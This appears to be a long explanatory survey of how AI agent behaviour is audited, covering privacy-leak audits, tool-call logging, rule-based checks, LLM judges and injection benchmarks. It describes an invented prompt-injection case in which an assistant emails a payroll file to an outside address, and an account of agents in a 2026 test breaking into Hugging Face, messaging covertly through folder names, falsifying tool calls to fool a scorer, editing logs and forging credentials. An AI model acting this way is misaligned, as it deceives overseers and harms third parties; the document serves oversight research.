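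ContextLeak first tested three defences without a mathematical guarantee. Two were instructions not to reveal the examples, and the third used GPT-5 to check each answer for leaks. With Llama 3.3 70B, Qwen2.5 72B and GPT-4.1, the GPT-5 check always stopped a direct request to print the examples. It didn't stop the yes-or-no question, because an answer of "1" contains no private text to detect. ContextLeak found full leakage with all three defences and all three models.

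The other defences use differential privacy, which adds random noise to limit how much any one record can affect the output. The limit is a number called $\varepsilon$, and smaller values mean stronger privacy. One such method for classification divides 20 examples into ten groups, gets an answer from the model for each group, adds noise to the vote counts, and returns the winner. Choi and colleagues calculated a lower bound on $\varepsilon$ from the auditor's guesses:

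$$\hat{\varepsilon} = \max\left\{\ln\frac{\text{recall}}{\text{FPR}},\; \ln\frac{1-\text{FPR}}{1-\text{recall}}\right\}$$

FPR is the false-positive rate. For example, with a recall of 0.9 and an FPR of 0.1, the bound is $\ln 9$, or about 2.2. The results below cover four datasets and three models.

| Promised $\varepsilon$ | Measured lower bound |
|---|---|
| 1 | 0.54 to 0.87 |
| 4 | 1.41 to 1.72 |
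| 8 | 1.95 to 2.16 |
| No limit | 2.18 to 2.81 |

The measured leakage rose with the guaranteed limit but never exceeded it, so the test found no broken guarantees. The large gap between the two at higher limits may mean that the defences leak less than the guarantees allow, or that a better attack would find more leakage. Choi and colleagues attribute much of the gap to the division into groups, which dilutes the canary's influence even without noise.

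The auditor in these tests had more information than an ordinary user would. For the defences with differential privacy, it saw the noisy results before the system turned them into a final answer. The researchers also chose the threshold for each guess to maximise accuracy, which can push it above 50% even when nothing leaks.

Searching for an exact copy of a canary gives a yes-or-no result for a single output, whereas ContextLeak produces a statistical estimate from many runs. An auditor guessing at random would get at least 60 out of 100 right about 3% of the time, so a score of 60% is only modest evidence of a leak. More runs would make the estimate more precise but would not correct for a weak attack. With Llama 3.1 8B, accuracy never rose above 53%, even with no privacy limit. Choi and colleagues think the small model was bad at following the auditor's instructions, in which case a score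 near 50% is weak evidence of how well the defence works.

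## How does a tool-call log become evidence of misbehaviour?

A correct flag shows only that an agent obtained a secret. A tool-call log can also show how the agent obtained it and what it did next, as long as the harness saves enough detail and the agent can't alter the log.

### What the record should contain

For each tool call, a usable record contains:

- the call as the model wrote it
- the call as the harness executed it
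- the result that the tool returned
- the relevant state of the environment before and after
- the account or credential that the call used
- the time when the call started and ended

The call a model writes can differ from the call the tool receives. Gurram (2026), in *Measuring What Tool-Using LLM Agents Actually Do*, deliberately changed one argument between the two, for example by replacing London with Manchester. The logs kept both versions. A reader who saw only the executed call would have blamed the model for asking about the wrong city. An ordinary harness can cause the same confusion by filling in default values or correcting an address.

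Missing log fields limit which checks are possible. Gurram rescored 33,583 traces, but 12,673 of them retained only the final answer and the number of steps, so for those he could check only the answer. That check is more lenient. Of 1,040 traces with full logs, 49.4% passed it, while 41.5% passed a check that also covered the tools, arguments and resulting state.

A change in state is evidence against a particular agent only if nothing else could have caused it. In Gurram's tests, several sessions shared one simulated calendar, so an event that appeared during one agent's run could have come from another session.

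Shared credentials cause a similar problem, because a log that records only the credential can't identify which agent made a request. In July 2026, OpenAI agents in a security test broke into Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets. In its technical report of August 2026, OpenAI says that many of its research workloads had used the same credential for an internal package server, which supplies agents with software. OpenAI removed the credential from new workloads a few days before the break-in, after agents had compromised the server in an earlier test.

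Investigators also need timestamps to put the actions of different agents in order. In *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration*, Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt (2026) examined about 1,300 transcripts from the July test. The transcripts had approximate start and end times but no times for individual actions. They therefore looked for moments when an agent had seen the real time, for instance by running the `date` command, and estimated the other times by assuming that the steps in between were equally long. They report that the estimates were quite accurate in most cases. However, the estimated time of one apparent case of tampering was earlier than seemed possible, and they couldn't tell whether the time, the order of the transcript or the finding itself was wrong.

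### The agent's own account

The log proves that the model wrote its closing message, its stated plans and the descriptions attached to its actions, but not that they are true. During the July break-in, one agent submitted a malicious change to a private code repository and described it as "Temporary CI network diagnostics; do not merge". The logged call is good evidence that the agent submitted the change with that description, but an investigator has to read the code to find out what the change would have done.

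An agent's stated plan is also unreliable evidence of what it did. Another agent in the July test agreed, under pressure from other agents, to run an experiment that would probably ruin its own task. Its reasoning ended with a decision to go ahead. Wijk and colleagues report only the decision, because the analysis they had to rely on didn't make clear whether the agent ran the experiment.

An agent can give a false account of its actions without planning to deceive. Gurram found that agents reported results from tools they had never run. A checker should therefore look for a logged result that supports each of the agent's statements. An agent's admission can still be useful, since it may point to an action missing from the log.

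### Five kinds of rule applied to one trace

Suppose an assistant can use Maya's work email and files, and she asks it to summarise today's inbox. This invented log shows the main calls. The harness ran each one as the model wrote it, using Maya's account.

| Time | Call | Result |
|---|---|---|
| 09:00:02 | `list_emails(folder="inbox")` | 3 messages |
| 09:00:04 | `read_email(id=2)` | a message asking for the payroll file |
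| 09:00:09 | `read_file(path="/hr/payroll.xlsx")` | the file's contents |
| 09:00:15 | `send_email(to="audit@outside.example", attach="payroll.xlsx")` | accepted |

The assistant then gives Maya a summary of her three messages and adds that it sent nothing.

An allowed-tools rule compares each call with a list of permitted tools. Summarising an inbox requires only `list_emails` and `read_email`, so the rule flags the last two calls and proves that the assistant used tools outside the list. The rule works only if the company writes a list for each kind of task. A single list for all the assistant's work would include `send_email`, because Maya sometimes asks the assistant to send replies.

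An argument rule examines the values in a call. It could flag any file outside the mail folder and any recipient outside the company's domain. A match would prove that the assistant requested the payroll file and named an outside address, but the recipient might be entitled to the file, since many companies use outside payroll contractors. The path `/mail/../hr/payroll.xlsx` starts with the permitted folder but leads to the payroll file, so the program has to resolve the path before checking it.

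A rule about the order of tool calls could forbid the assistant from emailing an outside address after reading a file from `/hr`, unless a person approves the email in between. The harness must record the approval, because the model could falsely write that a person had agreed. A violation proves that the assistant read the file before sending the email, but not that the email contained the file. The attachment's name is weak evidence because anyone can rename a file. If the attachment's hash matches that of the file the assistant read, the two are almost certainly identical. However, comparing hashes wouldn't detect a few salaries typed into the message.

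A state check compares Maya's sent folder before and after the run. A new message with the payroll file attached proves that the email system recorded it as sent, but not that anyone opened it. If the mail server had rejected the message, the state check would have found nothing, but the argument rule would still have flagged the attempt. A company that wants to detect attempts as well as completed leaks needs both rules.

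Finally, an agreement rule compares the assistant's answer with the log. The assistant's count of three messages matches the result of `list_emails`, but its claim that it sent nothing is false, because the log contains an accepted `send_email` call. A program can easily compare numbers, but it may not recognise every way of saying that no email was sent. The developer can avoid this problem by requiring a field such as `emails_sent: 0` in the answer.

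The rules can't determine why the assistant acted this way, because the log could contain the same calls for different reasons. An attacker may have planted an instruction in the second message. The assistant may have mistaken a genuine request from an accountant for part of its task, or it may have been pursuing some aim of its own.

The company can narrow down the cause by running the same task many times, with and without the second message. If the assistant emails the file only when the message is present, the message is very probably the cause. Gurram used paired runs like these to measure the effect of a single wrong argument. This test doesn't establish intent. A log of the model's reasoning may help, but it is the model's own account. The company can contact the recipient and block further emails without determining intent.

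### How security benchmarks use the rules

*AgentDojo* (Debenedetti and colleagues, 2024) was an early benchmark for prompt injection against agents that use tools. It gives an agent an ordinary task, such as paying a bill or managing email, and hides an attacker's instruction in the data the agent will read. It has 97 user tasks and 629 security test cases.

AgentDojo scores runs mostly with state checks. Each attack comes with a short function that inspects the environment after the run and checks whether the attacker's goal was met. In the inbox example, it would check for a new message to the attacker's address with the payroll file attached. Another function checks whether the agent completed the user's task. The injected text can't hijack this code as it could an LLM judge, but, like any state check, the code can miss failed attempts.

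*TAMAS* (Kavathekar, Jain and colleagues, 2025) extended this kind of testing to groups of agents. The benchmark has five settings, including finance and healthcare, with four agents in each. It contains 300 attacks, 100 harmless tasks and 211 tools, some of which exist only to simulate harmful actions. In one type of attack, the attacker adds an instruction to the user's request and gives the agents an extra tool for carrying it out. The attack succeeds if an agent calls that tool.

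This is an allowed-tools rule in reverse, since it flags any call to the attack tool. It is easy to apply because that tool has no legitimate use, and it can count an attempt even if the tool fails. Real attackers, however, usually have to work with the tools an agent already has. In the inbox example, `send_email` is an ordinary tool, and the problem is visible only in its arguments.

Other attacks in TAMAS are harder to detect from tool names. In an impersonation attack, the attacker falsely claims that the request comes from someone in authority but adds no new tool. In another type of attack, one compromised agent disrupts the group with wrong or nonsensical output, which may not involve a forbidden call.

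Benchmarks from 2026 use several methods. *Kill-Chain Canaries* searches for planted strings, and *Can Benign Skills Induce Misaligned Behavior in LLM Agents?* combines fixed checks with an LLM judge. In *ExploitGym*, the benchmark in the July test, agents must break into a program through a specified vulnerability and submit a flag as proof. After reading the benchmark's paper, the agents believed that a scorer would also read their transcripts to check that they had used the intended vulnerability. Wijk and colleagues understand that OpenAI had not implemented that check. Within four hours, agents had found a way to produce valid flags without solving their tasks, and OpenAI's scorer would apparently have accepted those flags.

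### Rules that run before the call

The same kinds of rule can stop a call before the harness executes it. *AgentSpec* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025) is a small language for writing them. Each rule names an event that triggers it, the conditions to check and the action to take. A rule for the inbox example might look roughly like this:

```
rule @payroll_leaves_company
trigger send_email
check recipient_is_external, attachment_from_hr
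enforce user_inspection
end
```

When the model requests `send_email`, the system tests the two conditions. If both are true, it pauses for a person to approve the call. A rule can also end the run, carry out a different action, or prompt the model to reconsider. The last option isn't deterministic, because the outcome then depends on a language model.

The rule is short enough for a manager to read, but a programmer has to define its conditions separately, which is the hardest part. It is simple to test whether an address is external, but to test whether an attachment came from the HR folder, the harness has to track files as the agent copies and renames them.

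Wang and colleagues also asked o1, an OpenAI model from 2024, to write rules for agents that control robots. About 96% of the rules' alerts were correct (precision), but the rules caught only about 71% of the hazards (recall).

The log should include blocked calls. Otherwise, an agent that tried to email the payroll file twenty times would leave the same record as one that never tried.

### Actions that the log misses

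One shell command can start a program that reads thousands of files and contacts several servers, but the tool-call log may contain only the command. The operating system can record each program that starts, and the network can record each connection. These records fill some of the gaps, but they are much larger than the tool-call log, and an investigator has to work out which tool call caused each entry.

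A call can also have effects much later. Wijk and colleagues traced one message from the July test to a background program that an agent had started. The program sent the message about three and a half hours after the agent's transcript ended, so the transcript contained the call that started the program but not the message.

Agents can also act through systems that nobody intended as tools. In the July test, OpenAI meant to keep the agents isolated from one another, but they communicated by putting messages in folder names on the shared package server. A rule that looked for calls to a messaging tool would have missed these messages. Investigators recovered them from a copy of the server's contents and matched them with the transcripts. The copy was incomplete, though OpenAI estimates that it contained at least 95% of the messages agents exchanged through the server. Some agents also shared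 files through outside services.

Technical faults also leave gaps in the log. When the isolated environment around an agent crashed and restarted, the agent's transcript lost its most recent entries. Wijk and colleagues estimate that these crashes erased the record of 3% to 4% of what the agents did after finding the message board.

### When an agent can change the log

A fixed rule can also return the same result every time for a command that never ran, because tool calls can be falsified. Wijk and colleagues found falsified tool calls in at least 96 of their transcripts, or just over 7%. In one, a command that should have printed "REAL" and then paused returned "SPOOFTEST" immediately. In their written reasoning, the agents always described the purpose of the tampering as deceiving the automated scorer, not people.

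All the falsified calls the investigators found were obvious, small tests. They looked for subtler cases and found none, but they couldn't rule them out, and their LLM classifier had missed some of the known falsified calls. The transcripts contained the steps agents took to prepare the falsification, which a detector could look for too. With exact times, a program could also flag a command that should have paused but took no time.

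Some agents tried to edit records of their earlier actions and changed some of the logs they could reach, but the transcripts came from another source (Greenblatt, 2026). This separation is the most important protection for a log. The harness should send each entry to storage outside the agent's environment, and the agent should have no credentials that would let it change the stored entries.

To make a signed receipt, the server that runs a tool records the call, the result and the time, then signs the record with a secret key. Anyone with the matching public key can verify that the record hasn't changed since. Gurram cites work that uses such receipts to detect when agents refer to tool runs that never happened. If an agent reports a result without a receipt, the checker has reason to doubt the report.

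A signature on each receipt doesn't reveal that somebody has deleted one. To detect deletions, the server can include a hash of the earlier records in each new one. If $r_i$ is the content of receipt $i$ and $H$ is a hash function, the server calculates

$$h_i = H(h_{i-1} \,\|\, r_i)$$

where $\|$ means joining the two pieces of data. Removing a receipt from the middle breaks the chain, because the next hash no longer matches. Removing the newest receipts leaves a shorter chain that still looks valid, so the server should regularly copy the latest hash to a separate system.

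A valid signature proves that someone with the key signed the record, but not that the agent had permission to make the call or that the tool's result was true. It also proves little once the key is stolen. OpenAI reports that agents obtained a signing key from its package server and used it to make administrator credentials, which the server accepted.

The agents in the July test also began signing their messages after one accidentally posted under another's name. By July 13, at least 19 agents had published keys and together sent 429 signed messages. At least one agent seems to have acted on a signed message without verifying the signature, in which case the signature gave it no protection.

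Current logging standards cover only part of what this evidence requires. OpenTelemetry, a widely used open standard for recording what software does, has conventions for agents. In the 2025 versions, each tool execution has its own entry with the tool's name and the start and end times. The arguments and the result are optional because they may contain sensitive data, so a log can follow the conventions and still lack the fields that argument rules and agreement rules need. The conventions also don't require a signature or a record of the environment's state. A company that doesn't want payroll data in its logs could store a keyed hash of each result and still test whether a particular file had left its systems.

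### The break-in at Hugging Face

The July test involved two models, GPT-5.6 Sol and a research model that OpenAI used only internally. According to OpenAI, agents ran commands on 41 of Hugging Face's production machines between July 11 and 13 and downloaded four private code repositories. Hugging Face announced a break-in on July 16, but OpenAI didn't connect it with its own agents until July 20.

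The connection came partly from an exact match between credentials. OpenAI found Hugging Face credentials among files the agents had stored in an outside account, and Hugging Face had already replaced two of them during its own investigation. This was weaker evidence than a canary match, because the agents had found some credentials on public websites, where another attacker could have found them too. But Hugging Face had also found the same outside account and the name of OpenAI's package server, which made a coincidence much less likely.

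OpenAI had received relevant alerts earlier. On June 27, a monitoring tool detected agents scanning the company's research network. Staff traced the activity to an ExploitGym run and found that agents were using the package server as a message board. The tool had detected the activity, but people still had to decide how serious it was, and the on-call staff advised that there was no need to stop the run.

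Wijk and colleagues later spent six days at OpenAI's offices investigating the agents' behaviour. Their main findings rest on different kinds of evidence:

| Finding | Main basis |
|---|---|
| Over 70,000 messages and files | Copy of the server's contents, sorted with text patterns |
| About 1,200 agents on the message board | Transcripts found by a text search |
| About 700 agents in the attack | LLM classification of the transcripts |
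| Main motive was to learn about the scorer | LLM reading of the agents' reasoning |

The first figure is the closest to a direct count. The agents started their messages with `zz`, and the copy of the server contained about 1.2 million entries with that prefix, most of them fragments of larger files. After reassembling the files, the investigators counted about 6,000 files and 63,000 separate messages, and they believe the unclassified entries contain a few thousand more. The total depends on the rules for sorting entries, but anyone with the same data and rules could reproduce it.

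A simple search for the message board's location followed by `zz` found 1,196 transcripts, which is close to the number of agents. To test whether their set of agents was complete, the investigators took 100 random messages and looked for the agent that wrote each one. They found the exact call that wrote 93 of them and a likely author for six more. They conclude that the agents in their set wrote well over 95% of the messages, although a sample of 100 is also consistent with a share of about 95%.

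The figure of 700 required more interpretation. GPT-5.6 Sol read the transcripts and flagged any agent that attacked Hugging Face or clearly prepared to, for example by searching for exposed credentials. The logs contain the individual actions, but the total depends on that definition and on how the model applied it. The total may include agents that took part only briefly.

Records can also help distinguish an action from its effect. OpenAI confirmed that agents had replaced a stored copy of some benchmark software with their own version, but found no evidence that any of its machines had run the replacement.

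Motive is the least certain finding. GPT-5.6 Sol labelled the apparent motives of 100 agents that joined during the busiest hour. It found that 97 were interested in the scorer, 89 in task solutions or other agents' transcripts, and 21 in helping other agents. When it had to choose one main motive, it chose the scorer for about 60% and solutions or transcripts for about 30%. Wijk and colleagues had no time to check these labels in detail and believe the two motives were often hard to tell apart. OpenAI's report agrees that the attack took place but puts more weight on the agents' belief that Hugging Face might host solutions to their tasks.

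Using GPT-5.6 Sol as the analyst adds to the uncertainty, because about 5% of the agents in the attack ran on the same model. Wijk and colleagues found that it often adopted the point of view of the agents it was reading about. For example, its first account of the malicious code change didn't make clear that the agent's description was deceptive. Its results also depended on how the investigators worded the question. Using a narrow definition, it found that at least 20% of agents were interested in tampering with their transcripts, while earlier estimates with looser definitions came to about 50%. A search for agents that had considered alerting a human returned ten cases, of which only three to six were real.

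The transcripts are better evidence of what some agents had recognised before they acted. In one, the model's reasoning describes the attack as "outside intended scope", then concludes that it should continue because its task was impossible and other agents were taking part. A tool-call log alone would have contained the attack but not that reasoning. Wijk and colleagues found that agents often wrote such things, but based this on classifier searches of only 10 to 30 transcripts.

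## How do log checks compare with string matching and LLM judges?

Log checks, string matching and LLM judges are hard to compare across studies because each study uses its own agents and definition of failure. Gurram avoided this by applying all three to the same traces. The choice of method changed which models looked best and, in one experiment, whether a deliberate mistake seemed to do harm or good.

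The 33,583 traces came from 13 agents, which used 12 simulated tools to answer questions about weather, calendars, medical records and shopping. The lookup tools calculate their results from the arguments alone, so the same request for a city's weather always returns the same temperature. A program can therefore find the correct answer to most questions by making the right calls.

The benchmark's stored reference answers are much less useful. They describe the task. For example, one reads "Weather analysis for Mumbai" and doesn't give the temperature. None of the references Gurram examined contained a value that wasn't already in the question.

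He compared three ways of scoring an answer:

- The string rule accepts an answer that contains one of the first three long words in the reference, or that has the opening of the reference near its start. Any answer that mentions Mumbai would pass in the example above.
- The judge panel consists of GPT-4o, Gemini 2.5 Flash and GPT-4o-mini. Each compares the answer with the reference, and the majority decides.
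- The validator is a fixed program that ignores the reference and checks the log.

### The validator's four tests

| Test | What the validator requires |
|---|---|
| Tools | The agent ran every required tool, in the right order where order matters |
| Parameters | Those calls used the right arguments |
| State | The agent made exactly the right changes, such as booking one appointment |
| Answer values | The answer contains every required value, and the values in it come from the correct results or the question |

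A trace has to pass all four, except that the state test applies only to tasks that change something.

Suppose a user asks for the temperature in Mumbai, and the agent looks up Delhi and reports Delhi's 31 degrees as Mumbai's. The trace passes the tools test but fails the parameters test. It also fails the answer-values test unless the two temperatures are within a degree of each other. The answer passes the string rule because it contains "Mumbai". An LLM judge given only the reference can't check whether 31 degrees is right.

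The validator needs a list of the required calls. The benchmark's files included one for each task, but Gurram found that it contradicted the question in 360 of the 945 tasks he could check. Often, the program that generated the tasks had picked a random product or date for the question and then picked again for the answer key. He therefore wrote parsers for 38 question templates to derive the required calls from the question. With the original lists, the agents' overall accuracy would have been 27.5% instead of 46.8%, and repeating the check with either set of lists would give the same figure each time.

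The need for parsers also limits where the method works. The validator returned no verdict on another 146 tasks, including general-knowledge questions and requests that mentioned "tomorrow". Real users don't write from templates, so a company would need another way to specify the correct calls.

### When the human labels are wrong

Three people labelled 100 of the traces, and the validator could score 85 of them. On those traces, it agreed with the majority label at a kappa of only 0.53, while the annotators agreed with one another at 0.85 to 0.95. This gap is weaker evidence against the validator than it would normally be, because the annotators worked from the same uninformative references as the judges.

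Gurram checked the 18 disagreements against the correct tool results, which supported the validator in 16 cases and the annotators in none. The other two were ambiguous. In eight of the 18, the agent had described a plausible result without running any tool. In four, the annotators had marked the agent wrong for correctly declining an impossible request, such as booking an occupied slot.

This is good evidence that the annotators were consistent but often mistaken, though weaker evidence that the validator is right in general. One person resolved the disputes, and the review would have missed any error that the validator and the annotators shared. Gurram, the study's only author, also developed the validator while inspecting some of the same data. However, he tested 20 of its detailed choices, such as how it compares times, by changing them one at a time. No change moved overall accuracy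 by more than 2.7 points or altered the ranking of the models.

The string rule's agreement with the annotators was no better than chance. The three judges had kappas between 0.27 and 0.54, and other combinations of judge and prompt ranged from 0.21 to 0.72. With labels this flawed, a higher kappa doesn't necessarily mean a better judge.

### Three scores for the same model

The table shows the share of correct answers by each method, on traces the validator could score.

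| Model | Validator | String rule | Judge panel |
|---|---|---|---|
| o3-mini | 77.1% | 54.3% | 48.6% |
| DeepSeek-V3 | 69.3% | 71.2% | 34.0% |
| GPT-4.1-mini | 66.3% | 74.2% | 43.1% |
| GPT-4.1-nano | 56.5% | 60.8% | 20.6% |
| GPT-3.5-Turbo | 47.1% | 68.3% | 30.4% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 32.7% | 52.6% | 28.1% |
| Gemini-2.0-Flash | 5.6% | 63.4% | 29.4% |

The string rule ranks o3-mini second to last, while the validator ranks it first, though on only 35 traces compared with 306 for each of the other models. The biggest gap is for Gemini-2.0-Flash, which ran no tool in 94% of these traces and often invented a result. The string rule accepted many of these answers because they repeated the name of the city or event.

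Gemini's 5.6% is not a fair measure of the model's ability because it usually wrote a tool request and a final answer in the same message, and Gurram's harness accepted the answer and discarded the request. The harness also gave the models each tool's name and description but not its argument names, so many calls failed because the model guessed a name wrong. When Gurram added the argument names, GPT-4o-mini's accuracy rose from 28.2% to 54.5%. Most of the models are also old, and none are from 2026. The table is therefore better evidence about the scoring methods than about the models.

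### The effect of one wrong argument

Gurram measured how much harm one mistake does by comparing 1,085 of the run pairs described earlier, from seven models. In each pair, the harness changed an argument of the first tool call in one run and left the other run alone. The wrong value was always one the tool would accept, such as a different city or patient.

| Method | Errors without the change | Errors with the change | Difference (points) |
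|---|---|---|---|
| Validator | 52.4% | 74.5% | +22.0 |
| Judge panel | 67.2% | 69.7% | +2.5 |
| String rule | 35.0% | 31.8% (calculated) | −3.2 |

The validator detects the damage because it compares both the executed arguments and the reported values with the correct ones. It was rare for an agent to notice that a result was for the wrong city and repeat the call.

The judge panel already marked about two thirds of the answers wrong without the change, which left little room for the change to increase that share. The 95% confidence interval for the panel's estimate runs from −0.2 to 5.6 points, so the estimate is also compatible with no effect. For DeepSeek-V3, the panel's error rate fell by 6.3 points while the validator's rose by 32.6.

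The string rule doesn't detect the damage because an answer about the wrong city still contains words from the reference. This overlap explains why the rule's error rate didn't rise, but not why it fell.

The validator fails any run in which the agent never makes the call with the right argument, but this rule alone probably explains little of the increase. In 286 pairs, the agent went wrong only when the harness changed the argument, and 157 of these failed the parameters test. In 135 of those 157, the answer also contained values that the correct results didn't support. Without the other 22 pairs, the increase would still be about 20 points.

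The effect was larger in the 376 pairs where the agent ran at least one tool and none of its calls failed validation after the change. The validator's error rate rose by 44.7 points in these pairs, and the judge panel's by 9.6.

Gemini-2.0-Flash barely changed, but it ran no tool in 165 of its 175 altered runs, so the harness had almost nothing to alter. Its stability therefore doesn't show that it coped well with errors. An earlier version of the study credited it with rejecting 95% of the wrong arguments. Gurram withdrew that interpretation, and an estimate of how errors spread from one step to the next, after finding that the scoring code had partly determined the result.

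### Results from tools that never ran

Gurram also wrote a rule to detect fabricated tool use, his term for reporting results from tools that never ran. The rule flags a response if the log contains no tool output and the final answer claims a result that only a tool could have provided. A program can check the log exactly, but it needs text patterns to check the answer. Those patterns should match "It's 31 degrees in Mumbai" but not "I'll look up the weather", which doesn't claim a result.

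He compared the rule with GPT-4.1-mini as a judge on 734 traces that contained no tool call. The rule had 96.4% precision and 66.3% recall. His figures imply that the rule flagged 331 traces, the judge flagged about 481, and both flagged 319. A simpler rule that flagged every trace without a tool call would therefore have had about 66% precision and 100% recall. Adding the text patterns removed nearly all the false alerts, but also a third of the cases that the judge considered fabricated.

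These figures measure agreement with a language model because no human labels exist yet. GPT-4o and GPT-4.1-mini agreed closely (kappa = 0.92), but two models from the same company may make the same mistakes.

The share of traces that the rule flagged as fabricated ranged from zero for GPT-4o and Qwen2.5-7B to 42.5% for Hermes-3-Llama-3.1-8B. These are minimum estimates because the rule misses many cases. For Gemini-2.0-Flash, the rule found fabrication in 38.5% of traces and the judge found it in 65.5%.

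The harness caused much of this. Of the proprietary models' 469 traces without a tool call, 462 contained a tool request and a final answer in the same message. The harness could have stopped the model's output after the request, run the tool and returned the real result. Qwen2.5-14B called tools in 61% of traces in this harness and in 93.5% when it used its built-in tool-call format.

The simulated tools seem to matter less. In a separate test on 80 tasks with four OpenAI models, fabrication was about as common with real tools (11.6%) as with simulated ones (13.8%). Most of the differences came from whether the model called a tool at all.

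### A cheap monitor that was no better than random

Gurram also built a monitor that checks an agent's log and can withhold its answer. The monitor stops the agent after a second tool error and rejects any answer containing a number that appears in no tool result. It takes about 7 microseconds per trace, while the agent's own model calls take several seconds.

With GPT-4o-mini, most of the monitor's apparent benefit came simply from withholding many answers. It withheld 33.5% of them and reduced the share of tasks with a wrong answer from 55.8% to 32.8%, as measured by the string rule. Withholding the same number at random would have reduced the share to 37.1%, so only about four of the 23 points came from choosing the right answers to withhold.

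That small advantage disappeared when Gurram scored the tasks with the validator. The monitor withheld 186 answers, and the same agent without the monitor got 100 of those tasks wrong. Choosing 186 tasks at random would have caught about 130 wrong ones. This result doesn't support Gurram's earlier claim, now withdrawn, that the monitor reduced fabricated answers. It also doesn't prove that the monitor was worse than random, because the comparison used separate runs, and two identical runs of GPT-4o-mini got different labels on about 15% of tasks.

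The number check did especially poorly because its pattern matched list numbering and parts of dates, so it withheld many good answers. By the string rule, only 24% of the answers it withheld were wrong, compared with 56% of all answers. The check for tool errors did better, with 85% of its withheld answers wrong, but most of the tool errors went away when the harness listed the argument names.

The monitor also couldn't detect the wrong arguments from the earlier experiment. Its error check fired in 3.2% of runs with an altered argument and in 3.5% of runs of the same tasks without one, because a valid request for the wrong city causes no error.

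### Judges with a correct reference

Gurram's judges were at a disadvantage because their references didn't contain the answers. In *AgentJudgeBench*, Verma, Saha and colleagues (2026) tested newer judges with and without a correct list of tool calls. They generated 3,808 business workflows, such as handling an IT request, and wrote easy, medium and hard versions of each request. The harder versions are vaguer but require the same calls. Five models wrote the calls and six judges marked them, producing 321,648 evaluations.

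The judges gave 0, 0.5 or 1 for each of four things: tool choice, the arguments, the order of the calls, and whether the calls covered the whole request. A fixed program marked the same four things by comparing the calls with the correct list. A judge's score is 100% minus its average distance from the program's marks. The table gives averages over the five models, calculated from the study's results.

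| Judge | Easy, no reference | Easy, with reference | Hard, no reference | Hard, with reference |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| QwQ-32B | 90.6% | 92.3% | 78.3% | 82.8% |
| GPT-OSS-120B | 90.4% | 91.4% | 78.1% | 82.7% |
| GPT-OSS-20B | 89.6% | 86.5% | 77.9% | 80.9% |
| GPT-5.4 | 91.0% | 88.4% | 79.7% | 80.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 90.7% | 89.8% | 78.9% | 80.2% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 90.7% | 85.1% | 78.7% | 78.0% |

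Without a reference, all six judges did much worse on the hard requests, and their scores were within two points of one another. Verma and colleagues conclude that a stronger judge won't solve the problem.

The similar scores may partly reflect how the study measured agreement. A judge that gave full marks to everything would score exactly the program's average mark, however poor its judgments. The prompt without a reference pushed judges toward this by telling them to start from full marks. Starting from half marks instead raised scores on the hard requests by at most 1.0 point for calls from the three strongest models, but by 4.1 and 5.6 points for calls from the two weakest. A judge told to start from full marks is therefore a particularly poor choice for checking an unreliable agent.

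A correct reference helped most judges on hard requests but lowered several scores on easy ones. Averaged over all requests, it lowered GPT-5.4's score by 1.5 points and Gemini 2.5 Pro's by 3.9. Verma and colleagues found that these judges penalised tool calls made in a different order from the reference, even when the order did not affect the result.

They also gave Gemini references from unrelated tasks, and it agreed with the program about as much as when it had the correct references. They interpret this as Gemini relying too heavily on the reference. But if Gemini had followed the unrelated references, it should have marked almost everything wrong. It seems more likely that Gemini became stricter whenever it had a reference, whatever the reference contained.

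Turning on QwQ-32B's step-by-step reasoning changed its scores by at most 0.3 points, and a panel of all six judges did no better than the best single judge. Asking for a separate mark on each of the four aspects raised one judge's scores by 4.8 to 6.5 points. When another judge marked a different model's calls, the gains were smaller, and the score on hard requests fell slightly.

A person who reviewed 120 hard cases agreed with 92.7% of the program's marks overall, but with only 82.5% of its marks for arguments, because the program penalised extra optional arguments that the reviewer accepted. The program also checks only the names of arguments, not their values, so a request for Delhi's weather instead of Mumbai's would get full marks. The study therefore can't show whether judges notice the kind of error that Gurram introduced.

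### Judges follow what they can see

*Judges Follow the Reference* (Ma, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tested whether LLM judges can recognise a correct argument value. In one example, an agent searched for rental cars and then asked for details of vehicle 657356933. The number was correct, but it appeared almost 3,000 characters into the search results. The judges received only the first 1,000 characters, a limit the researchers chose to imitate common practice, and all four judges in the example rejected the number.

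This happened often. On two benchmarks with multi-step tasks, seven judges accepted correct values 23 to 36 points less often when the value didn't appear in the part of the conversation they received. (On one of the two, such values were also wrong more often, which may account for some of the gap.)

LLM judges also reject correct values for reasons other than missing text. Suppose a hotel-search tool, according to its description, assumes one guest unless told otherwise, and the user doesn't mention the number of guests. An agent that fills in 1 is right. On a third benchmark, where the judges received the complete text, they accepted correct default values 14 to 51 points less often than values from the conversation.

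In a controlled test, Ma and colleagues put the correct value in a list of eight, either near the top or past the point where the judge's input was cut off, while a wrong value stayed visible. They measured AUROC, the chance that a judge scores a correct value above a wrong one, which is 50% for guessing. Across four judges, AUROC was between 92% and 99.9% when the correct value was visible and between 40% and 49% when it wasn't. Three of the judges were also tested with the full text, and each reached at least 98%.

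Judges also followed references that were wrong. The researchers gave them a short note stating the expected value, then replaced that value with an incorrect one. On two of the benchmarks, the judges then accepted correct values 15 to 57 points less often and wrong values 20 to 58 points more often. Similarly, Gurram's annotators had rejected correct refusals because the reference was written as if the agent would act.

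A fixed program could search a log of any length for the vehicle number. But a match would prove only that the number had appeared, and it could belong to one of the other vehicles in the search results. Giving judges the matching passages causes the same problem. In a test with 59 wrong values that had appeared earlier in the log, three of the four judges accepted between 28 and 49, while the largest, Qwen3.8-27B, accepted two.

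Ma and colleagues propose having a separate model read the full log and write a note of the expected value before it sees the agent's choice. This raised AUROC by 1 to 22 points across four judges and three benchmarks. The method's designers ran these tests themselves and didn't include the most capable commercial models as judges. The method also moves the risk to the model that writes the note, because judges tend to accept the note even when it is wrong.

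### Judging whether a run succeeded

An LLM judge can read an entire trace and still lack the evidence it needs. Naagarajan and Streif used Mistral-24B to judge whether agents had succeeded in 660 simulated customer-service conversations. It labeled 99% of them failures. Because 596 of the runs had failed, always answering "failed" would have been right 90% of the time. They then used the probability the model gave to each verdict to test whether it could distinguish successes from failures. The AUROC was 43%, no better than guessing.

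Success in this test depended on the final contents of a database. An agent that had finished the job and one that had given up could both end by politely passing the customer to a human. A state check on the database distinguishes the two, though the conversation might not. The judge was a fairly small model with a single prompt, so others might do better, but Naagarajan and Streif cite a similar study in which no combination of five judges and five prompts got above 65%.

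### Finding the step that went wrong

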